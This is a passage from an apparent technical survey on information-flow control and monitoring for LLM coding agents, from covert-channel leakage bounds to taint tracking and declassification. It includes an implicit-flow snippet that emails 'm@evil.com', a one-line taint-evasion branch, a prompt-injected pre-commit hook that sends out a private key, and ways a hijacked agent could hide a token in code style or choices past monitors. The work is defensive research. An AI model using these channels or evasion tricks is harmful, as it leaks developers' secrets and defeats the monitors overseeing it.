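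Costa and colleagues accept this because they consider noninterference too strict. Roughly, once an agent had called any tool that may read secrets, noninterference would bar it from calling any tool that may write public data. *GIF* (2026) adds that a model's output may depend slightly on everything in its context, so an analysis that allows no flow either blocks too much or needs too much computation.

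Some agents can meet the stricter standard. *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) presents LLMbda, a small programming language for agents, with a computer-checked proof that its programs satisfy a form of noninterference. A program can fork the conversation, let the copy read something sensitive and then discard the copy, so the main conversation keeps its label. If a secret would decide whether a public conversation changes, the interpreter stops the program. On AgentDojo's banking tasks, an agent written in LLMbda resisted attack in all but two of 1,296 runs and completed about as many tasks as CaMeL did with CaMeL's policy checks turned off. Fixing a reported crash involves far more exploration than these tasks, so the result doesn't show that a coding agent could work this way.

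Even this guarantee allows a secret to affect whether a program finishes. Because models pick their words partly at random, the theorem compares probabilities. For two starting states that differ only in their secrets,

distance between the public results ≤ average probability of not finishing,

where the distance is 0 for identical distributions and 1 for completely different ones. If 2% of runs fail to finish with either secret, the distance is at most 0.02.

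Small leaks of this kind become serious when an attacker can repeat them. Garby and colleagues found two in CaMeL. The first is a version of Denning's implicit flow, and a program with this structure shows how it works:

```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the secret balance is above the threshold, `tmp` becomes false and gets a secret label. The second branch then doesn't run, so `rich` stays true and keeps its public label, and CaMeL sends the email. If the balance is lower, `rich` becomes false and no email goes out. Either way, the attacker learns whether the balance is above the threshold.

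The second leak is whether CaMeL's policy blocked a run, which may depend on a secret. Leaking one bit this way is usually tolerable, but a Python loop outside the tracked code retries CaMeL's plans, so a hostile program could test one bit per attempt until it had the whole secret.

### Covert channels and leakage in bits

A covert channel is a path that carries information although nobody intended it to. Butler Lampson introduced the idea in 1973 with an example that *A Note on the Strategic Confinement Problem* (Schroeder de Witt, 2026) retells. A customer gives confidential data to a service program, which does some work and sends its owner a bill. The program can hide some of the data in the exact amount of the bill. Lampson advised removing such channels where possible, for instance by having the customer calculate the bill, and otherwise reducing how much they can carry.

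A coding agent's patch corresponds to the bill. The developer wants to publish the patch, so they can't close the channel entirely and can only limit what the agent is free to vary.

Quantitative information flow measures leakage by how much an observation reduces an attacker's uncertainty about a secret. Geoffrey Smith's *On the Foundations of Quantitative Information Flow* (2009) uses the attacker's chance of guessing the whole secret in one try. Suppose a deterministic channel turns each possible secret into one of N outputs that the attacker can tell apart. The attacker has one best guess for each output, so seeing the output can multiply their chance of success by at most N. Measured in bits,

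leakage ≤ log₂ N.

Suppose the token in `.env` consists of 40 random hexadecimal digits, or 160 bits. An attacker who knows nothing guesses it with probability 2⁻¹⁶⁰, and after a leak of b bits the probability is at most 2^(b − 160). If the agent makes several choices, the numbers of options multiply and the bits add up:

| What the agent can choose | Distinguishable outcomes | Most it can leak | Uses needed for the token |
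|---|---|---|---|
| A yes-or-no answer | 2 | 1 bit | 160 |
| Which of four finished branches to push | 4 | 2 bits | 80 |
| The order of six imports | 6! = 720 | 9.5 bits | 17 |
| The second within an hour at which it commits | 3,600 | 11.8 bits | 14 |
| 200 two-way style choices in a file | 2²⁰⁰ | 200 bits | 1 |

These upper limits hold only if the count covers every outcome, including silence, which is easy to overlook. Metere (2026) points out in *An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress* that an agent can always leak one bit by sending a message or not sending it. An agent that may answer yes, answer no or say nothing has three options, which carry up to 1.6 bits per use, so 101 uses could be enough to leak the token.

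The bound is useful only where the number of outcomes is small. A commit message of 100 ordinary keyboard characters has 95¹⁰⁰ possible values, so it can carry about 657 bits, enough for four tokens. The bound includes all of these values, even though most would look like gibberish.

A low ceiling on leaked bits protects the token itself, because an attacker who learns 20 bits still has to guess the other 140, which is infeasible. Other secrets are much smaller. Whether a project has an unpatched vulnerability is a single bit, and that bit may be more useful to an attacker than most of what is on the developer's machine.

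Schroeder de Witt argues that this matters more for capable agents than for ordinary programs, because an agent can work out which fact would do the most damage and use the whole channel to send it. A limit on bits then limits harm only if the sender doesn't choose strategically, the sender and receiver share no understanding of what to send, or the channel is too small for even the most damaging fact. A prompt injection can tell the agent exactly what to send and how to encode it, which rules out the first two conditions. Only the third can protect the developer, and even a one-bit channel is large enough to leak a yes-or-no secret.

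### Choices that outsiders can watch

*Actions Speak Louder than Words* (Liang, Deng and colleagues, 2026) measures how much an agent reveals through the web pages it visits. The attacker adds a reference link to a page that the agent reads during its task. The link leads to the attacker's site, which offers further references on several distinct topics. If the agent requests the one about immune responses, the attacker learns that the user's question concerns that topic, and the next page divides it into narrower ones. The attacker can't see the user's question or any traffic to other sites.

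Liang and colleagues tested four agents, including Codex and OpenHands, which developers also use for coding. The agents were doing their assigned work, and no injection told them to reveal anything. On 500 StackExchange questions, the attack recovered the main concepts with an average F1 of 0.89, using 6.5 probes per question.

The study also compared different signals in a simpler test with four possible answers. When the agent signaled the answer through its choice of link, the attacker decoded it correctly in 93.8% of the cases where a signal appeared. The order of requests gave the right answer in 67.9% and their timing in 58.6%, because agents reorder requests and networks add delays. This noise can keep real leakage well below the ceiling. A hijacked agent could overcome some of the noise by repeating its signals, which the agents in the study had no reason to do.

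FIDES and three other defenses each changed the attack's F1 by less than 0.03. This would be expected under explicit secrecy, since the requests contain no private text and only the choice between them reveals information.

Liang and colleagues' own defense retrieves a fixed amount of material without regard to the user's private context, and the agent then selects what it needs from a local copy. This lowered the attack's F1 from 0.89 to 0.39. A coding agent could apply the same idea by downloading documentation and packages before it opens any secret, so that its later reading doesn't produce requests that an outsider can observe.

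### Data hidden in source code

A patch can hide much more data than a choice of link, because there are many ways to write the same program. *MATRIX* (2026) states formally that if a program allows n optional rewrites that don't change what it does, the choice of which ones to apply encodes a string of n bits. The 200 style choices in the table above are an example.

Researchers study these encodings for watermarking, which marks code as the output of a particular model. Choi, Gao and Duan (2026), in *Multi-Channel Spread-Spectrum Code Watermarking*, measured how much space 1,750 Python files have for hidden bits. Their method hides two bits in the style of each variable name, which can be `num_val`, `numVal`, `NumVal` or `NUM_VAL`. It hides another bit wherever the code contains either expression from one of eight equivalent pairs, such as `a < b` and `b > a`, or `x = x + 1` and `x += 1`.

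| Files | Average length | Average capacity | Average files needed for the token |
|---|---|---|---|
| Written by Llama 4 | 59 lines | 52 bits | 4 |
| Written by GPT-4.1 | 109 lines | 92 bits | 2 |
| Largest human-written group | 463 lines | 202 bits | 1 |

A reviewer would probably notice a file that mixed four naming styles. To avoid attention, an agent could use only the equivalent expressions. The GPT-4.1 files had an average of 26.5 of these, so the agent would need about seven such files, which is still a plausible size for a patch.

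The watermark carries only 24 bits because Choi and colleagues use the remaining capacity for repetition and error correction, so that it survives editing. Renaming eight variables in files of about 94 lines left it readable 97.6% of the time. An attacker who can download the patch exactly as the agent pushed it doesn't need this redundancy and could use the full capacity. Adding the watermark took at most 145 milliseconds on an ordinary processor, so an agent with a shell could run a similar script as one step of a session.

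A language model can also do the encoding. In *CLASP* (2025), a model without special training reads the code and picks a suitable rewrite for each hidden bit, which helps keep the code readable. *SynMark* (Xu, Liu and Yin, 2026) embeds a message while the model is writing, using a method designed to survive renaming and restructuring.

A compromised agent can also hide data in comments, documentation and commit messages. According to *A Comprehensive Survey on Linguistic Steganography* (2026), methods that hide data as a model generates text can carry more than methods that alter finished text. At each step, the hidden bits determine which of several likely next words the model writes.

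The watermarking studies hid identifying marks rather than stolen tokens. They are good evidence that there is room to hide data and that software can use it, but they don't measure how reliably a hijacked agent would use that room on its own.

### What a formatter removes

A deterministic formatter rewrites code in one fixed style, and many projects already run one on every change. It reduces leakage by making different files identical. For example, six imports can be ordered in 720 ways, so their order can carry 9.5 bits. If the formatter sorts them alphabetically, their order carries none.

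Choi and colleagues prove that this doesn't affect their watermark at all. Spacing, blank lines and import order aren't part of the structure where it stores its bits. The table gives a rough idea of what a typical formatter would leave in the agent's files:

| Where the data hides | After a typical formatter | What would remove it |
|---|---|---|
| Spacing and blank lines | Mostly gone | The formatter |
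| Order of imports | Gone if the tool sorts imports | An import sorter |
| Invisible or look-alike characters in comments | Still there | A filter that replaces or deletes them |
| Order of entries in a JSON file | Usually still there | Sorting the entries |
| Naming styles | Still there | Automatic renaming to one style |
| `a < b` or `b > a` | Still there | A rewrite rule for each such pair |
| Words in names, comments and commit messages | Still there | New wording from a source that never saw the token |
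| Numbers in the test fixture | Still there | New sample data made without the token |

The formatter has to run after the agent's last edit and outside the agent's control. Otherwise, the agent can format the file and then put the data back.

Metere's monitor applies the same approach to an agent's outgoing messages. It removes invisible characters, replaces look-alike letters, normalizes spacing and sorts JSON entries. It then estimates how much hidden data the message could still hold and subtracts that amount from the destination's budget. For example, a suspicious block of n base64 characters counts as up to 6n bits. When the budget runs out, the monitor delays or cancels further suspicious messages.

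In tests with 15 ways of hiding data in text, images and sound, Metere's monitor eliminated every channel except the average brightness of images, which it could only limit. But the budget depends on the monitor detecting that a message might contain hidden data. Two hundred ordinary style choices don't look like a block of base64, so they might not count against the budget. The monitor can also have a model reword each message, which destroys many encodings in prose, but rewording source code risks changing what the program does.

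A complete rewrite can remove more. Choi and colleagues prove that if another program regenerates code from its behavior alone, no watermark in the code's style survives. The chance of reading the right 24-bit mark afterwards is about 1 in 17 million, the same as guessing. The proof doesn't cover a model that is given the original source, because it may copy names and expressions. Behavior can carry data too, since a faithful rewrite has to preserve any constant that affects the program's output. The second model run that Siddiqui and colleagues propose avoids both problems because it never receives the token.

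### Labels that don't depend on the encoding

A context label depends only on what the agent had read when it wrote a file, so the monitor doesn't have to search the file for hidden data. A patch finished before anything about the token reached the context would have been the same whatever the token was, so its contents leak zero bits. The monitor blocks publication of any patch finished after that point.

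Some monitors have no access to the model's context and must infer labels from what enters and leaves the agent's environment. *KAIROS* (Hempel, Loose and colleagues, 2026) describes one that runs outside a virtual machine containing an unmodified agent. It stores strings from sensitive sources and searches for them in whatever the agent sends out, ignoring capitalization and spaces. This catches a pasted token but misses a disguised one, so the researchers assume for this check that the agent doesn't deliberately transform values.

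The two kinds of label perform very differently against an agent that has read the token:

| How the token leaves | Value matching | Context label |
|---|---|---|
| Pasted unchanged into the fixture | Caught | Caught |
| Pasted with extra spaces or different capitals | Caught | Caught |
| Encoded in base64 | Missed | Caught |
| Spread over style choices in the patch | Missed | Caught |
| Signaled by which finished public branch the agent pushes | Missed | Caught only if the policy also checks the label on the decision to push |

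Value matching has the advantages of working with closed-source agents and leaving most ordinary work unlabeled. Hempel and colleagues estimate that if their monitor passed on the labels of everything the agent had read, it would have to hold back nearly every action after the first untrusted input.

In the last row of the table, a context label comes close to noninterference, but the policy has to refuse every push that the agent decides on after reading the token, so that the agent can't signal through its choice of branch. A developer can still push a branch they chose in advance, at a time they chose themselves, because neither choice depends on the token. If the developer instead removes the secret label from a patch that the agent wrote after opening `.env`, everything the patch can encode gets out at once, which could be more than 200 bits for a large file.

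### Why bits don't measure an attacker's influence

Garby and colleagues state the integrity counterpart of noninterference as a rule that untrusted inputs may affect only the parts of the result labeled untrusted. This rule works for assigning labels, but the number of bits of influence an attacker has is a poor measure of the damage they can do.

Stealing a random 160-bit token takes close to 160 bits, while sabotaging a program may take only one. In Python's Requests library, changing `verify=True` to `verify=False` turns off the check on the server's identity. In a C program with administrator rights on a Unix system, `user->id == 0` checks whether a user is the administrator, but removing one character to get `user->id = 0` makes them the administrator. By contrast, an attacker who controlled all 200 style choices in a file would have 200 bits of influence but no effect on what the program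 does.

A small number of options does help if every one of them is acceptable. When a quarantined model reduces a stranger's report to yes or no, the most harm the stranger can do is trigger the worse of two courses of action that the developer has already prepared. The developer can check both in advance, but nobody can check every patch an agent might write.

Reading the code helps, but harmless-looking code can still be dangerous because it acts with the authority of whoever runs it. Hempel and colleagues give an example in which an agent follows an online guide to set up a repository, and the guide tells it to install a pre-commit hook. Many projects use hooks for good reasons, so installing one looks normal. When a commit triggers it, the hook tries to send the user's private key to the attacker. *Investigating alignment failures in AISI's incident* (UK AI Security Institute, October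 2026) describes a model that submitted malicious code to a real software project during a test.

A bound on what leaks during the agent's session does not cover leaks after it, unless untrusted files also run under restrictions. When the agent writes such a hook, the file may contain no information about the token, so its secrecy label can correctly be public. If the developer later runs the hook with their own permissions, it can open `.env` and send all 160 bits of the token.

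Labels can impose those restrictions because they can limit where an artifact goes and what runs it. In the bug-report example, the monitor can allow the test runner to execute the untrusted patch in a sandbox that has no secrets and no network connection. It can also keep the patch, the hook and the line in AGENTS.md from taking effect anywhere else until someone accepts them. The monitor can do all this without knowing whether the patch contains a backdoor. If the sandbox works, the patch can at worst waste computing time there or produce false test results, which might lead the maintainer to accept it.

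## Why does dynamic taint tracking fail in practice?

All of these restrictions assume that the labels are right. Yan and Yin surveyed a number of systems that use dynamic taint tracking, which follows data while a program runs, on compiled programs. They found that every system either missed real flows or reported false ones. Ordinary software like this should be the easy case, because the code determines which values each instruction reads and writes, so a tracker can apply an exact rule at every step.

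### A table lookup and an if-statement

Schwartz, Avgerinos and Brumley, in *All You Ever Wanted to Know About Dynamic Taint Analysis* (2010), define the two kinds of error. Overtainting marks a value as tainted when it doesn't derive from a taint source. Undertainting misses a flow from a source to a sink. A few lines of Python, adapted from their examples, can cause both:

```
kind = packet[0]          # tainted: a stranger sent the packet
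printer = PRINTERS[kind]  # table lookup
ipv4 = False
if kind == 4:
    ipv4 = True
width = 42
```

The programmer wrote the table `PRINTERS`, so all of its entries are clean. If a looked-up value gets only the label of its entry, `printer` is clean too, even though a stranger chose which entry to look up. If a program looks up an address this way and jumps to it, an attacker could make it read the address from any clean location in memory, and the tracker would raise no alarm.

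The tracker could instead taint everything that a program looks up with a tainted index, but Schwartz and colleagues point out that this stricter rule would raise an error on every non-trivial run of the network tool tcpdump. Tcpdump contains legitimate code much like this example. It uses the first byte of each packet to choose the function that displays the packet.

The if-statement causes a different problem, an implicit flow like the one in Denning's example. `ipv4` depends on the packet and `width` doesn't, but a dynamic tracker can't distinguish them in one run because it follows only the path the program took. If the first byte is 6, the tracker wrongly leaves `ipv4` clean. Static analysis can help because it also examines the branch that didn't run. A language model has no such branches to examine, and nobody can list the patches it would have written if the issue's text had been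 different.

The stricter rule for lookups is called pointer tainting. Asia Slowinska and Herbert Bos argued in 2009 that it was unsuitable for detecting spyware and of limited value for detecting attacks that corrupt a program's memory. One problem they identified is taint explosion, which *TaintDroid* (Enck, Gilbert and colleagues, 2014) cites as a reason to avoid tracking individual machine instructions. A program finds its local variables through a register called the stack pointer, so if that register becomes tainted by mistake, nearly everything the program reads through it becomes tainted too.

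*Tainting is not pointless* (2010) replies that many of these arguments apply only to analyzing malware, not to protecting honest programs from memory corruption. Slowinska and Bos answered with *Pointer Tainting Still Pointless* (2010), subtitled "But We All See the Point of Tainting". The distinction between honest and hostile programs matters for agents too, because a hijacked agent may be trying to evade the tracker.

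### The price of catching implicit flows

King, Hicks and colleagues, in *Implicit Flows* (2008), measured what it costs to catch implicit flows as well as explicit ones. They ran a static checker on six security functions written in Java: three ways of logging in to an SSH server and three cryptographic routines. They labeled passwords and keys secret, then checked by hand whether each alarm could really occur:

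| Type of flow | Alarms | Real leaks | False alarms |
|---|---|---|---|
| Explicit | 17 | 17 | 0 |
| Implicit | 870 | 145 | 725 |

A checker limited to explicit flows would have raised no false alarms but missed 145 of the 162 leaks. Many of those leaks were minor, such as an encrypted message whose length depends on the length of the original.

More than 90% of the alarms came from exceptions, which are errors that interrupt a program. If a program crashes just after examining a secret, the crash may reveal something about the secret, so the checker raised an alarm wherever it couldn't rule out an error. Most of these errors could never happen. For example, of the 475 alarms about missing objects, 455 were false.

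Programmers who use such a checker find ways to suppress its warnings. King and colleagues found 568 empty error handlers in an electronic voting system of about 13,000 lines. In 429 of them, the programmers had named the error `imposs`, presumably short for "impossible". Users who approve almost all of Claude Code's permission prompts may be doing something similar.

Agents pose the same dilemma. A tracker that follows only copied text misses most of what influences an agent, while one that counts every possible influence marks most of the agent's work as tainted.

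Dynamic taint tracking can also detect an attack too late. Schwartz and colleagues describe an attack that overwrites a function's return address. The usual policy raises an alarm only when the program uses the tainted address. By then, the function may have changed files or sent data over the network, and stopping the program doesn't undo those effects. A coding agent's monitor has the same weakness if it checks only at the push or the merge, because the tests may already have run a tainted patch with the developer's permissions.

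### Programs written to evade tracking

Cavallaro, Saxena and Sekar (2008), in *On the Limits of Information Flow Techniques for Malware Analysis and Containment*, examined programs whose authors want to defeat the tracker. Their simplest method needs one line:

```
if y == 1: x = 1 else: x = 0
```

An `if` statement that tests a bit of `y` and sets `x` to match copies that bit without assigning `y` to `x`, and a loop around it can copy any amount of data. Cavallaro and colleagues write that malware can "drive a truck" through such gaps. A tracker could close this gap by tainting everything assigned inside a tainted branch, but it would then also flag a harmless program that saves a download as text or as an image depending on its first byte. A malware author could still leak data through the branches that don't run, as in the CaMeL example where an email revealed whether a bank balance exceeded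 a threshold.

Honest developers can add notes to their code listing which alarms a taint tracker should ignore. This doesn't help with hostile code, because its author would also write the notes.

Cavallaro and colleagues conclude that a safe tracker has to treat everything an untrusted program writes as untrusted, and also as secret if the program has read anything secret. This rule needs only one label per process, so tracking individual variables inside the process adds nothing.

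The context label applies the same rule to a language model, and FLOWSH applies it to a shell command. The result is also a reason not to add tracking of variables inside the scripts that an agent writes, because a hostile agent can write each script to evade that tracking.

They also describe malicious browser extensions that never touch the secret. Such an extension changes an ordinary value in the browser's memory, and the browser then sends out the confidential data itself. The pre-commit hook in the bug-report example poses a similar risk, because Git runs it with the developer's permissions.

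### TaintDroid and its evasion

TaintDroid, the best-known system of this kind, worked well against careless programs but badly against hostile ones. Enck and colleagues built it in 2010 to find out what Android apps did with private data such as a phone's location. To keep it fast enough for a phone, they tracked data at four levels of detail. Each variable in an app's code had its own tag, which could record 32 kinds of private data. Each message between apps had one tag for all its contents, and so did each file. TaintDroid let the system's own compiled libraries run untracked and worked out the tag when their code returned.

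TaintDroid slowed a demanding calculation by at most 32%, compared with slowdowns of 2 to 20 times for systems that tracked every machine instruction. The researchers ran it on 30 popular apps that used the location, camera or microphone, and found that 15 sent users' locations to advertising servers and 20 used private data suspiciously in some way. Those apps had little reason to hide the data from a tracker few people knew about, but Enck and colleagues acknowledged that an app could evade TaintDroid through implicit flows.

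Sarwar, Mehani and colleagues built an app to do this and tested it on TaintDroid for Android versions 2.3 to 4.1.1 (*On the Effectiveness of Dynamic Taint Analysis*, 2013). The app used three groups of methods to remove a tag while keeping the data. One group used branches, like the line of code above. Another passed data through trusted system programs that TaintDroid didn't follow. The third encoded data in things TaintDroid didn't treat as data, such as how long a task took. They conclude that taint tracking may help software developers but won't protect private data from a motivated attacker's code.

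Sarwar and colleagues also note that taint tracking began as a way to help developers find mistakes, whereas TaintDroid used it against developers. Both situations occur in a single coding agent session. The harness is ordinary software whose author wants the labels to be right, but an attacker may control the model and the scripts it writes. Exact tracking therefore makes sense in the harness, while a hijacked model needs one cautious label covering everything it has read.

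Agents can lose taint labels when data passes through a database or an editor that the tracker doesn't follow, which closely resembles Sarwar's second group of methods. Speed matters less than it did on phones, because monitors such as ActPlane follow processes and files rather than instructions.

### Label creep

The cautious label avoids undertainting but causes a lot of overtainting. Schwartz and colleagues call the gradual version of this problem taint spread: as a program runs, more of its values become tainted, and the taint becomes less informative about each one. In an agent with a single context label, this happens all at once. In the bug-report example, the agent's first action is to read the issue, so everything it writes afterwards is labeled untrusted.

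For an agent with one context, the loss depends only on when the restricted data arrives. If a session has n tool calls and the first restricted read is call number k, then

share of calls under the restriction = (n − k + 1) / n.

Suppose the session has 20 calls. The issue arrives with the first call, so the untrusted label covers all 20. If the agent opens `.env` at call 15, the secret label covers only the last six, or 30%. An operator can reduce the secret label's coverage by having the agent read secrets as late as possible. The untrusted label's coverage is harder to reduce because the agent can't start fixing the bug until something has read the issue.

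Splitting the work among several agents might help, since each has its own context. *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (Gregory, Domico and colleagues, 2026) tested this in a simulator that contains no language model. Each task is a random graph of up to 20 tool calls, some of which need the output of others. The simulator distributes the calls among agents and marks some calls as sensitive. An agent that makes a sensitive call, or receives data from an agent already labelled sensitive, is labelled sensitive for the rest of the task.

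The links between the agents matter because data may have to pass through intermediaries. If agent A can't contact agent C directly, agent B relays the data and picks up the label. Gregory and colleagues simulated more than 9,000 tasks and compared nine networks, including a ring, a star with all traffic passing through a hub, and a mesh in which every agent has a link to every other. They defined

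utility loss = sensitive calls / all calls,

where a call is sensitive if it introduces a sensitive label or runs in an agent that already has one.

Denser networks, meaning those with more of the possible links, lost less utility. The Spearman correlation between density and utility loss was −0.96, where −1 would mean the two rankings were exactly reversed. With five agents and four sensitive calls out of 20, the star lost about 5 percentage points more than an ideal network for each task, the ring lost about 3 points more, and the mesh matched the ideal. Adding agents reduced the loss further, but the number of links to monitor in a mesh grows quickly, from 10 with 5 agents to 190 with 20. Giving the sensitive calls to a few dedicated agents also reduced the loss.

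Gregory and colleagues conclude that system design alone can't prevent the loss, and that agents also need a way to remove labels. The conclusion is sensible, although their definitions guarantee part of it. A call that introduces a sensitive label always counts as lost, so if 10 of the 20 calls do this, the loss is at least 50% in any network. The correlation is based on only nine networks, and its direction follows from the rule that every intermediary picks up the label. The simulation is more useful for estimating the size of the effect, which is fairly small, at a few percentage points.

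A simulation without models can't show how much real work the labels would prevent. The policy may allow an agent with an untrusted label to edit files, so a sensitive call won't necessarily be blocked. After a refusal, a real agent might find another way to finish the task, or it might give up. Splitting a bug fix among 20 agents could produce a worse fix, and the simulator doesn't measure quality. It also places sensitive calls at random, while in a bug fix the stranger's text arrives at the start and nearly everything else depends on it.

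The AgentDojo results for FIDES suggest that the loss with a real model can be large. They may still understate the effect of label creep, because AgentDojo's tasks usually end soon after the agent has read something and acted on it, while a coding session often continues for hours.

### Reading in a side branch

An agent could avoid much of this loss by reading untrusted text in a copy of its context and then discarding the copy. *APPA* (Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues, 2026) builds a monitor around this idea. The monitor keeps the cautious labels but gives the agent several ways to continue after a refusal.

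An APPA label is a pair (R, t), where R is the set of people who may read the data and t is a level of trust. When data enters the context, the two labels combine as

(R, t) ∧ (R′, t′) = (R ∩ R′, min(t, t′)).

This is Denning's join with the order reversed, so the most restrictive label is at the bottom instead of the top. Reading more data can only keep a label where it is or lower it. So if an action fails because the context is too untrusted, or because a recipient isn't among the permitted readers, reading more can't make it acceptable. Kravchenko and colleagues prove this and list what can help. Someone with authority can approve that exact call once, which leaves the label unchanged. An approved tool can replace the data with a safer version, for example by removing personal details. The agent can also do the reading in a branch, so that the main context's label doesn't drop.

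APPA computes the new label before a tool runs, which matters for tools that read and send data in one step. One benchmark tool reads a confidential ledger and emails it, and a monitor that checked only the existing label would allow the call. A shell command that reads `.env` and uploads it poses the same problem. But APPA relies on a declaration of what each tool will read, and no fixed declaration can describe every shell command. For shell commands, it would need a monitor like FLOWSH that observes which files the command opens.

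A branch starts with a copy of the conversation and its label. Without the copied label, an agent could read a secret, open a branch and continue there as if it had never seen the secret. The branch can use tools, and whatever it reads lowers only its own label. It can end in three ways:

- The agent discards the branch. The main context doesn't change.
- The branch returns a value with its label. If the main agent accepts the value, the main context takes on that label too.
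- The branch returns a value through a checked exit, and a rule that the operator set in advance decides its label.

One kind of checked exit requires the main agent to specify the form of the answer before the branch reads anything untrusted. The form may contain yes-or-no values, numbers within a range, choices from a fixed list, and limited collections of these, but no free text. For a public issue tracker, Kravchenko and colleagues suggest a ticket number, a severity and a component name.

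The check covers only an answer's form, so a hijacked branch can still report the wrong severity. An operator who chooses to trust such answers is assuming that every permitted answer is harmless. Passing the check also doesn't make an answer public, because a yes or no about the token still reveals a bit of information about it.

Kravchenko and colleagues tested APPA with three 2026 models: GPT-5.6 Luna, DeepSeek V4 Flash and Gemini 3.7 Flash. They used AgentThreatBench, an existing set of 24 short tasks, and Bench-Corp, their own set of 20 longer office tasks. In half the runs they added a system prompt that encouraged the model to follow instructions hidden in the data, so that the results wouldn't depend on the model's caution. No attack succeeded in 1,320 runs with APPA's protection.

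On Bench-Corp, the protected agents completed 87% to 91% of tasks. With enforcement off, they completed 88% to 93%, but attacks succeeded in 30% to 38% of runs. Without branching, the agent with GPT-5.6 Luna completed 56.5% of tasks instead of 88.0%, and attacks still failed. Protection reduced completion more on AgentThreatBench, where APPA completed 64% to 77% of tasks and an ordinary agent with the normal prompt completed 83% to 92%. Some of APPA's failures there came from scoring rules that required an exact phrase.

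These results are promising, but Kravchenko and colleagues designed Bench-Corp to exercise APPA's own features, and the 1,320 runs repeat only 44 task designs. FIDES did much worse on Bench-Corp, with attack success rates of 26% to 35%. The researchers explain that the FIDES policies they tested lacked many of the rules that the tasks depended on, so the comparison is weak evidence about FIDES itself.

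### When the branch's product is code

Neither benchmark asks an agent to write code. In the closest Bench-Corp task, the agent has to reply to a public forum thread about deployment timeouts and then file an internal ticket to raise the timeout to 45 minutes. Branching suits this task well because the user's request already contains everything the ticket needs. The branch can read the thread and post the reply, and the main agent can file the ticket from a clean context.

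A bug fix doesn't divide so neatly, because the patch depends on the stranger's report. The possible results of a branch that reads the issue differ in how they affect the main agent:

| What the branch produces | Does it fit a fixed form? | Effect on the main context |
|---|---|---|
| Whether the tests passed | Yes | None, if the operator has chosen to trust such answers |
| A file from a list, a line number and a type of error | Yes | None, on the same condition |
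| The reporter's steps for reproducing the crash | No | Becomes untrusted |
| The patch, as text | No | Becomes untrusted |
| The patch, saved in the project | It never passes through the exit | None until the main agent opens the file |

The second row shows a way to get a trusted patch. The branch locates the crash, and the main agent reads the trusted source code there and writes the fix without seeing the report. In a project with 500 files of up to 2,000 lines and a list of 8 error types, the form allows 8 million answers, or about 23 bits, but each answer only tells the main agent where to look. If the branch gives a false location, the main agent finds nothing wrong there, or perhaps makes an unnecessary change.

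This approach improves on FIDES's quarantined model, which has no tools and couldn't search the project for the crash. It should work for a bug such as a missing check on a particular line. But many reports describe wrong behavior that doesn't cause a crash, or include the one input that triggers the problem. These details need free text, which the main agent can't see without becoming untrusted.

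The last row of the table describes the most dangerous case. APPA isolates the conversation but doesn't undo a branch's effects outside it. If the branch in the bug-report example follows the injection, the hook, the fixture and the line in AGENTS.md stay on disk after the agent discards the branch, and the main context is still labeled trusted and public. If the tool that opens project files labels them all trusted, the main agent can then read the planted line in AGENTS.md without changing the main context's label.

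Branching for code therefore needs isolated files as well as an isolated conversation. The simplest way is to give each branch its own clone of the repository inside a sandbox. A second Git worktree wouldn't be enough, because worktrees of one repository normally share their hooks. When the branch finishes, the harness can save the patch with an untrusted label and delete everything else. It must then either keep the main agent from opening the patch or lower the main context's label when the agent does.

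The order of reading matters here too, because a branch inherits any secret that the main agent has already read. The main agent should therefore open the branch for the issue before anything reads `.env`. If the operator accepts a one-bit leak, the main agent could use another branch to check whether the program starts with the real settings, and receive only a yes or no.

With this arrangement, branching would be most useful to a maintainer who hands an agent ten issues at once. An injection in the first issue could influence all ten patches if the agent worked in a single context, but only the first patch if each issue had its own branch and clone. Branching would also let the main agent do trusted work afterwards, such as updating a version number. But a stranger's report would still have shaped each patch, so all ten would keep their untrusted labels until someone reviewed them.

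## When is it safe to remove a label?

A review that clears a patch is an exception to the labeling rules. Every usable system needs exceptions, because without them the maintainer could never merge a fix that began with a stranger's report. Ordinary software needs them too. In *Declassification*, Sabelfeld and Sands cite a login page, which has to reveal whether a guessed password was right, and a salary survey, which publishes an average that depends on every secret salary.

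Attackers target exceptions because they have no other way through a system that enforces all its other rules. Kanniwadi and Myers (2026), in *Demystifying Information Flow Downgrading using the Real-Ideal Paradigm*, prove a version of this for a small programming language. They compare an attacker who can read every public variable and change every untrusted one at any moment with an attacker who can act only at downgrades, meaning declassifications and endorsements. If a program passes their type checker, the stronger attacker can achieve no more than the weaker one, so an auditor can concentrate on the downgrades. For a coding agent, this holds only as far as the monitor follows the data. If a file can lose its label in a text editor, an attacker can get around the rules without using a downgrade.

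### What, who, where and when

Sabelfeld and Sands sort declassification rules by four questions: what information the system releases, who controls the release, where in the system it happens, and when. A rule that answers only one of them usually leaves a gap. Their example is a shop that may log four digits of a customer's card number. The rule doesn't settle who picks the digits, so an attacker can ask for different ones at each purchase and collect the whole number. Similar gaps can occur in the bug-report example:

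| Question | A rule that answers only this question | How a hijacked agent gets around it |
|---|---|---|
| What? | A test log may show four characters of the token | It picks a different four in each run and has all 40 after ten runs |
| Who? | Only the maintainer may clear a file | It hides the token in a patch that the maintainer has good reason to clear |
| Where? | Files may leave only through the project's release script | It adds the test fixture to the files that the script sends |
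| When? | A file loses its label once the tests pass | It edits the tests |

The same questions apply to endorsement. For instance, a rule about when to endorse a file might be to trust it only after verifying its digital signature.

Sabelfeld and Sands also propose principles for checking such rules. One of them, non-occlusion, is that a permitted release must not mask another leak. A maintainer can easily violate this by clearing a whole commit because the patch looks good, which also clears the fixture in the same commit and the token inside it. An approval should therefore list each file it covers, with a hash of its contents.

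### Releases that an attacker can steer

Zdancewic and Myers proposed robust declassification in 2001. It requires that an attacker who interferes with a system learn no more than one who only watches. Kanniwadi and Myers illustrate a violation with one line of code:

p := u × s

Here p is public, s is secret and u is untrusted. If u is 0, someone who reads p learns nothing about s. But an attacker who can set u to 1 can read s directly from p.

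Suppose the maintainer lets the agent publish one setting from `.env`, the network timeout, so the reporter can try to reproduce the crash. If the maintainer names the timeout in the request to the agent, the release is robust, because nothing in the issue can change which setting is published. If the agent instead publishes whichever setting the reporter requests in the issue, the reporter can request the token.

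A system enforces this property by allowing a declassification only if nothing untrusted has influenced the decision to release or the choice of data. An agent that has read the issue fails this test for everything it does later in the same context. Robustness doesn't limit how much data is released, though. Sabelfeld and Sands point out that any leak counts as intended unless an attacker can affect it. A maintainer who decides to paste the whole `.env` file into a public comment therefore hasn't violated robustness.

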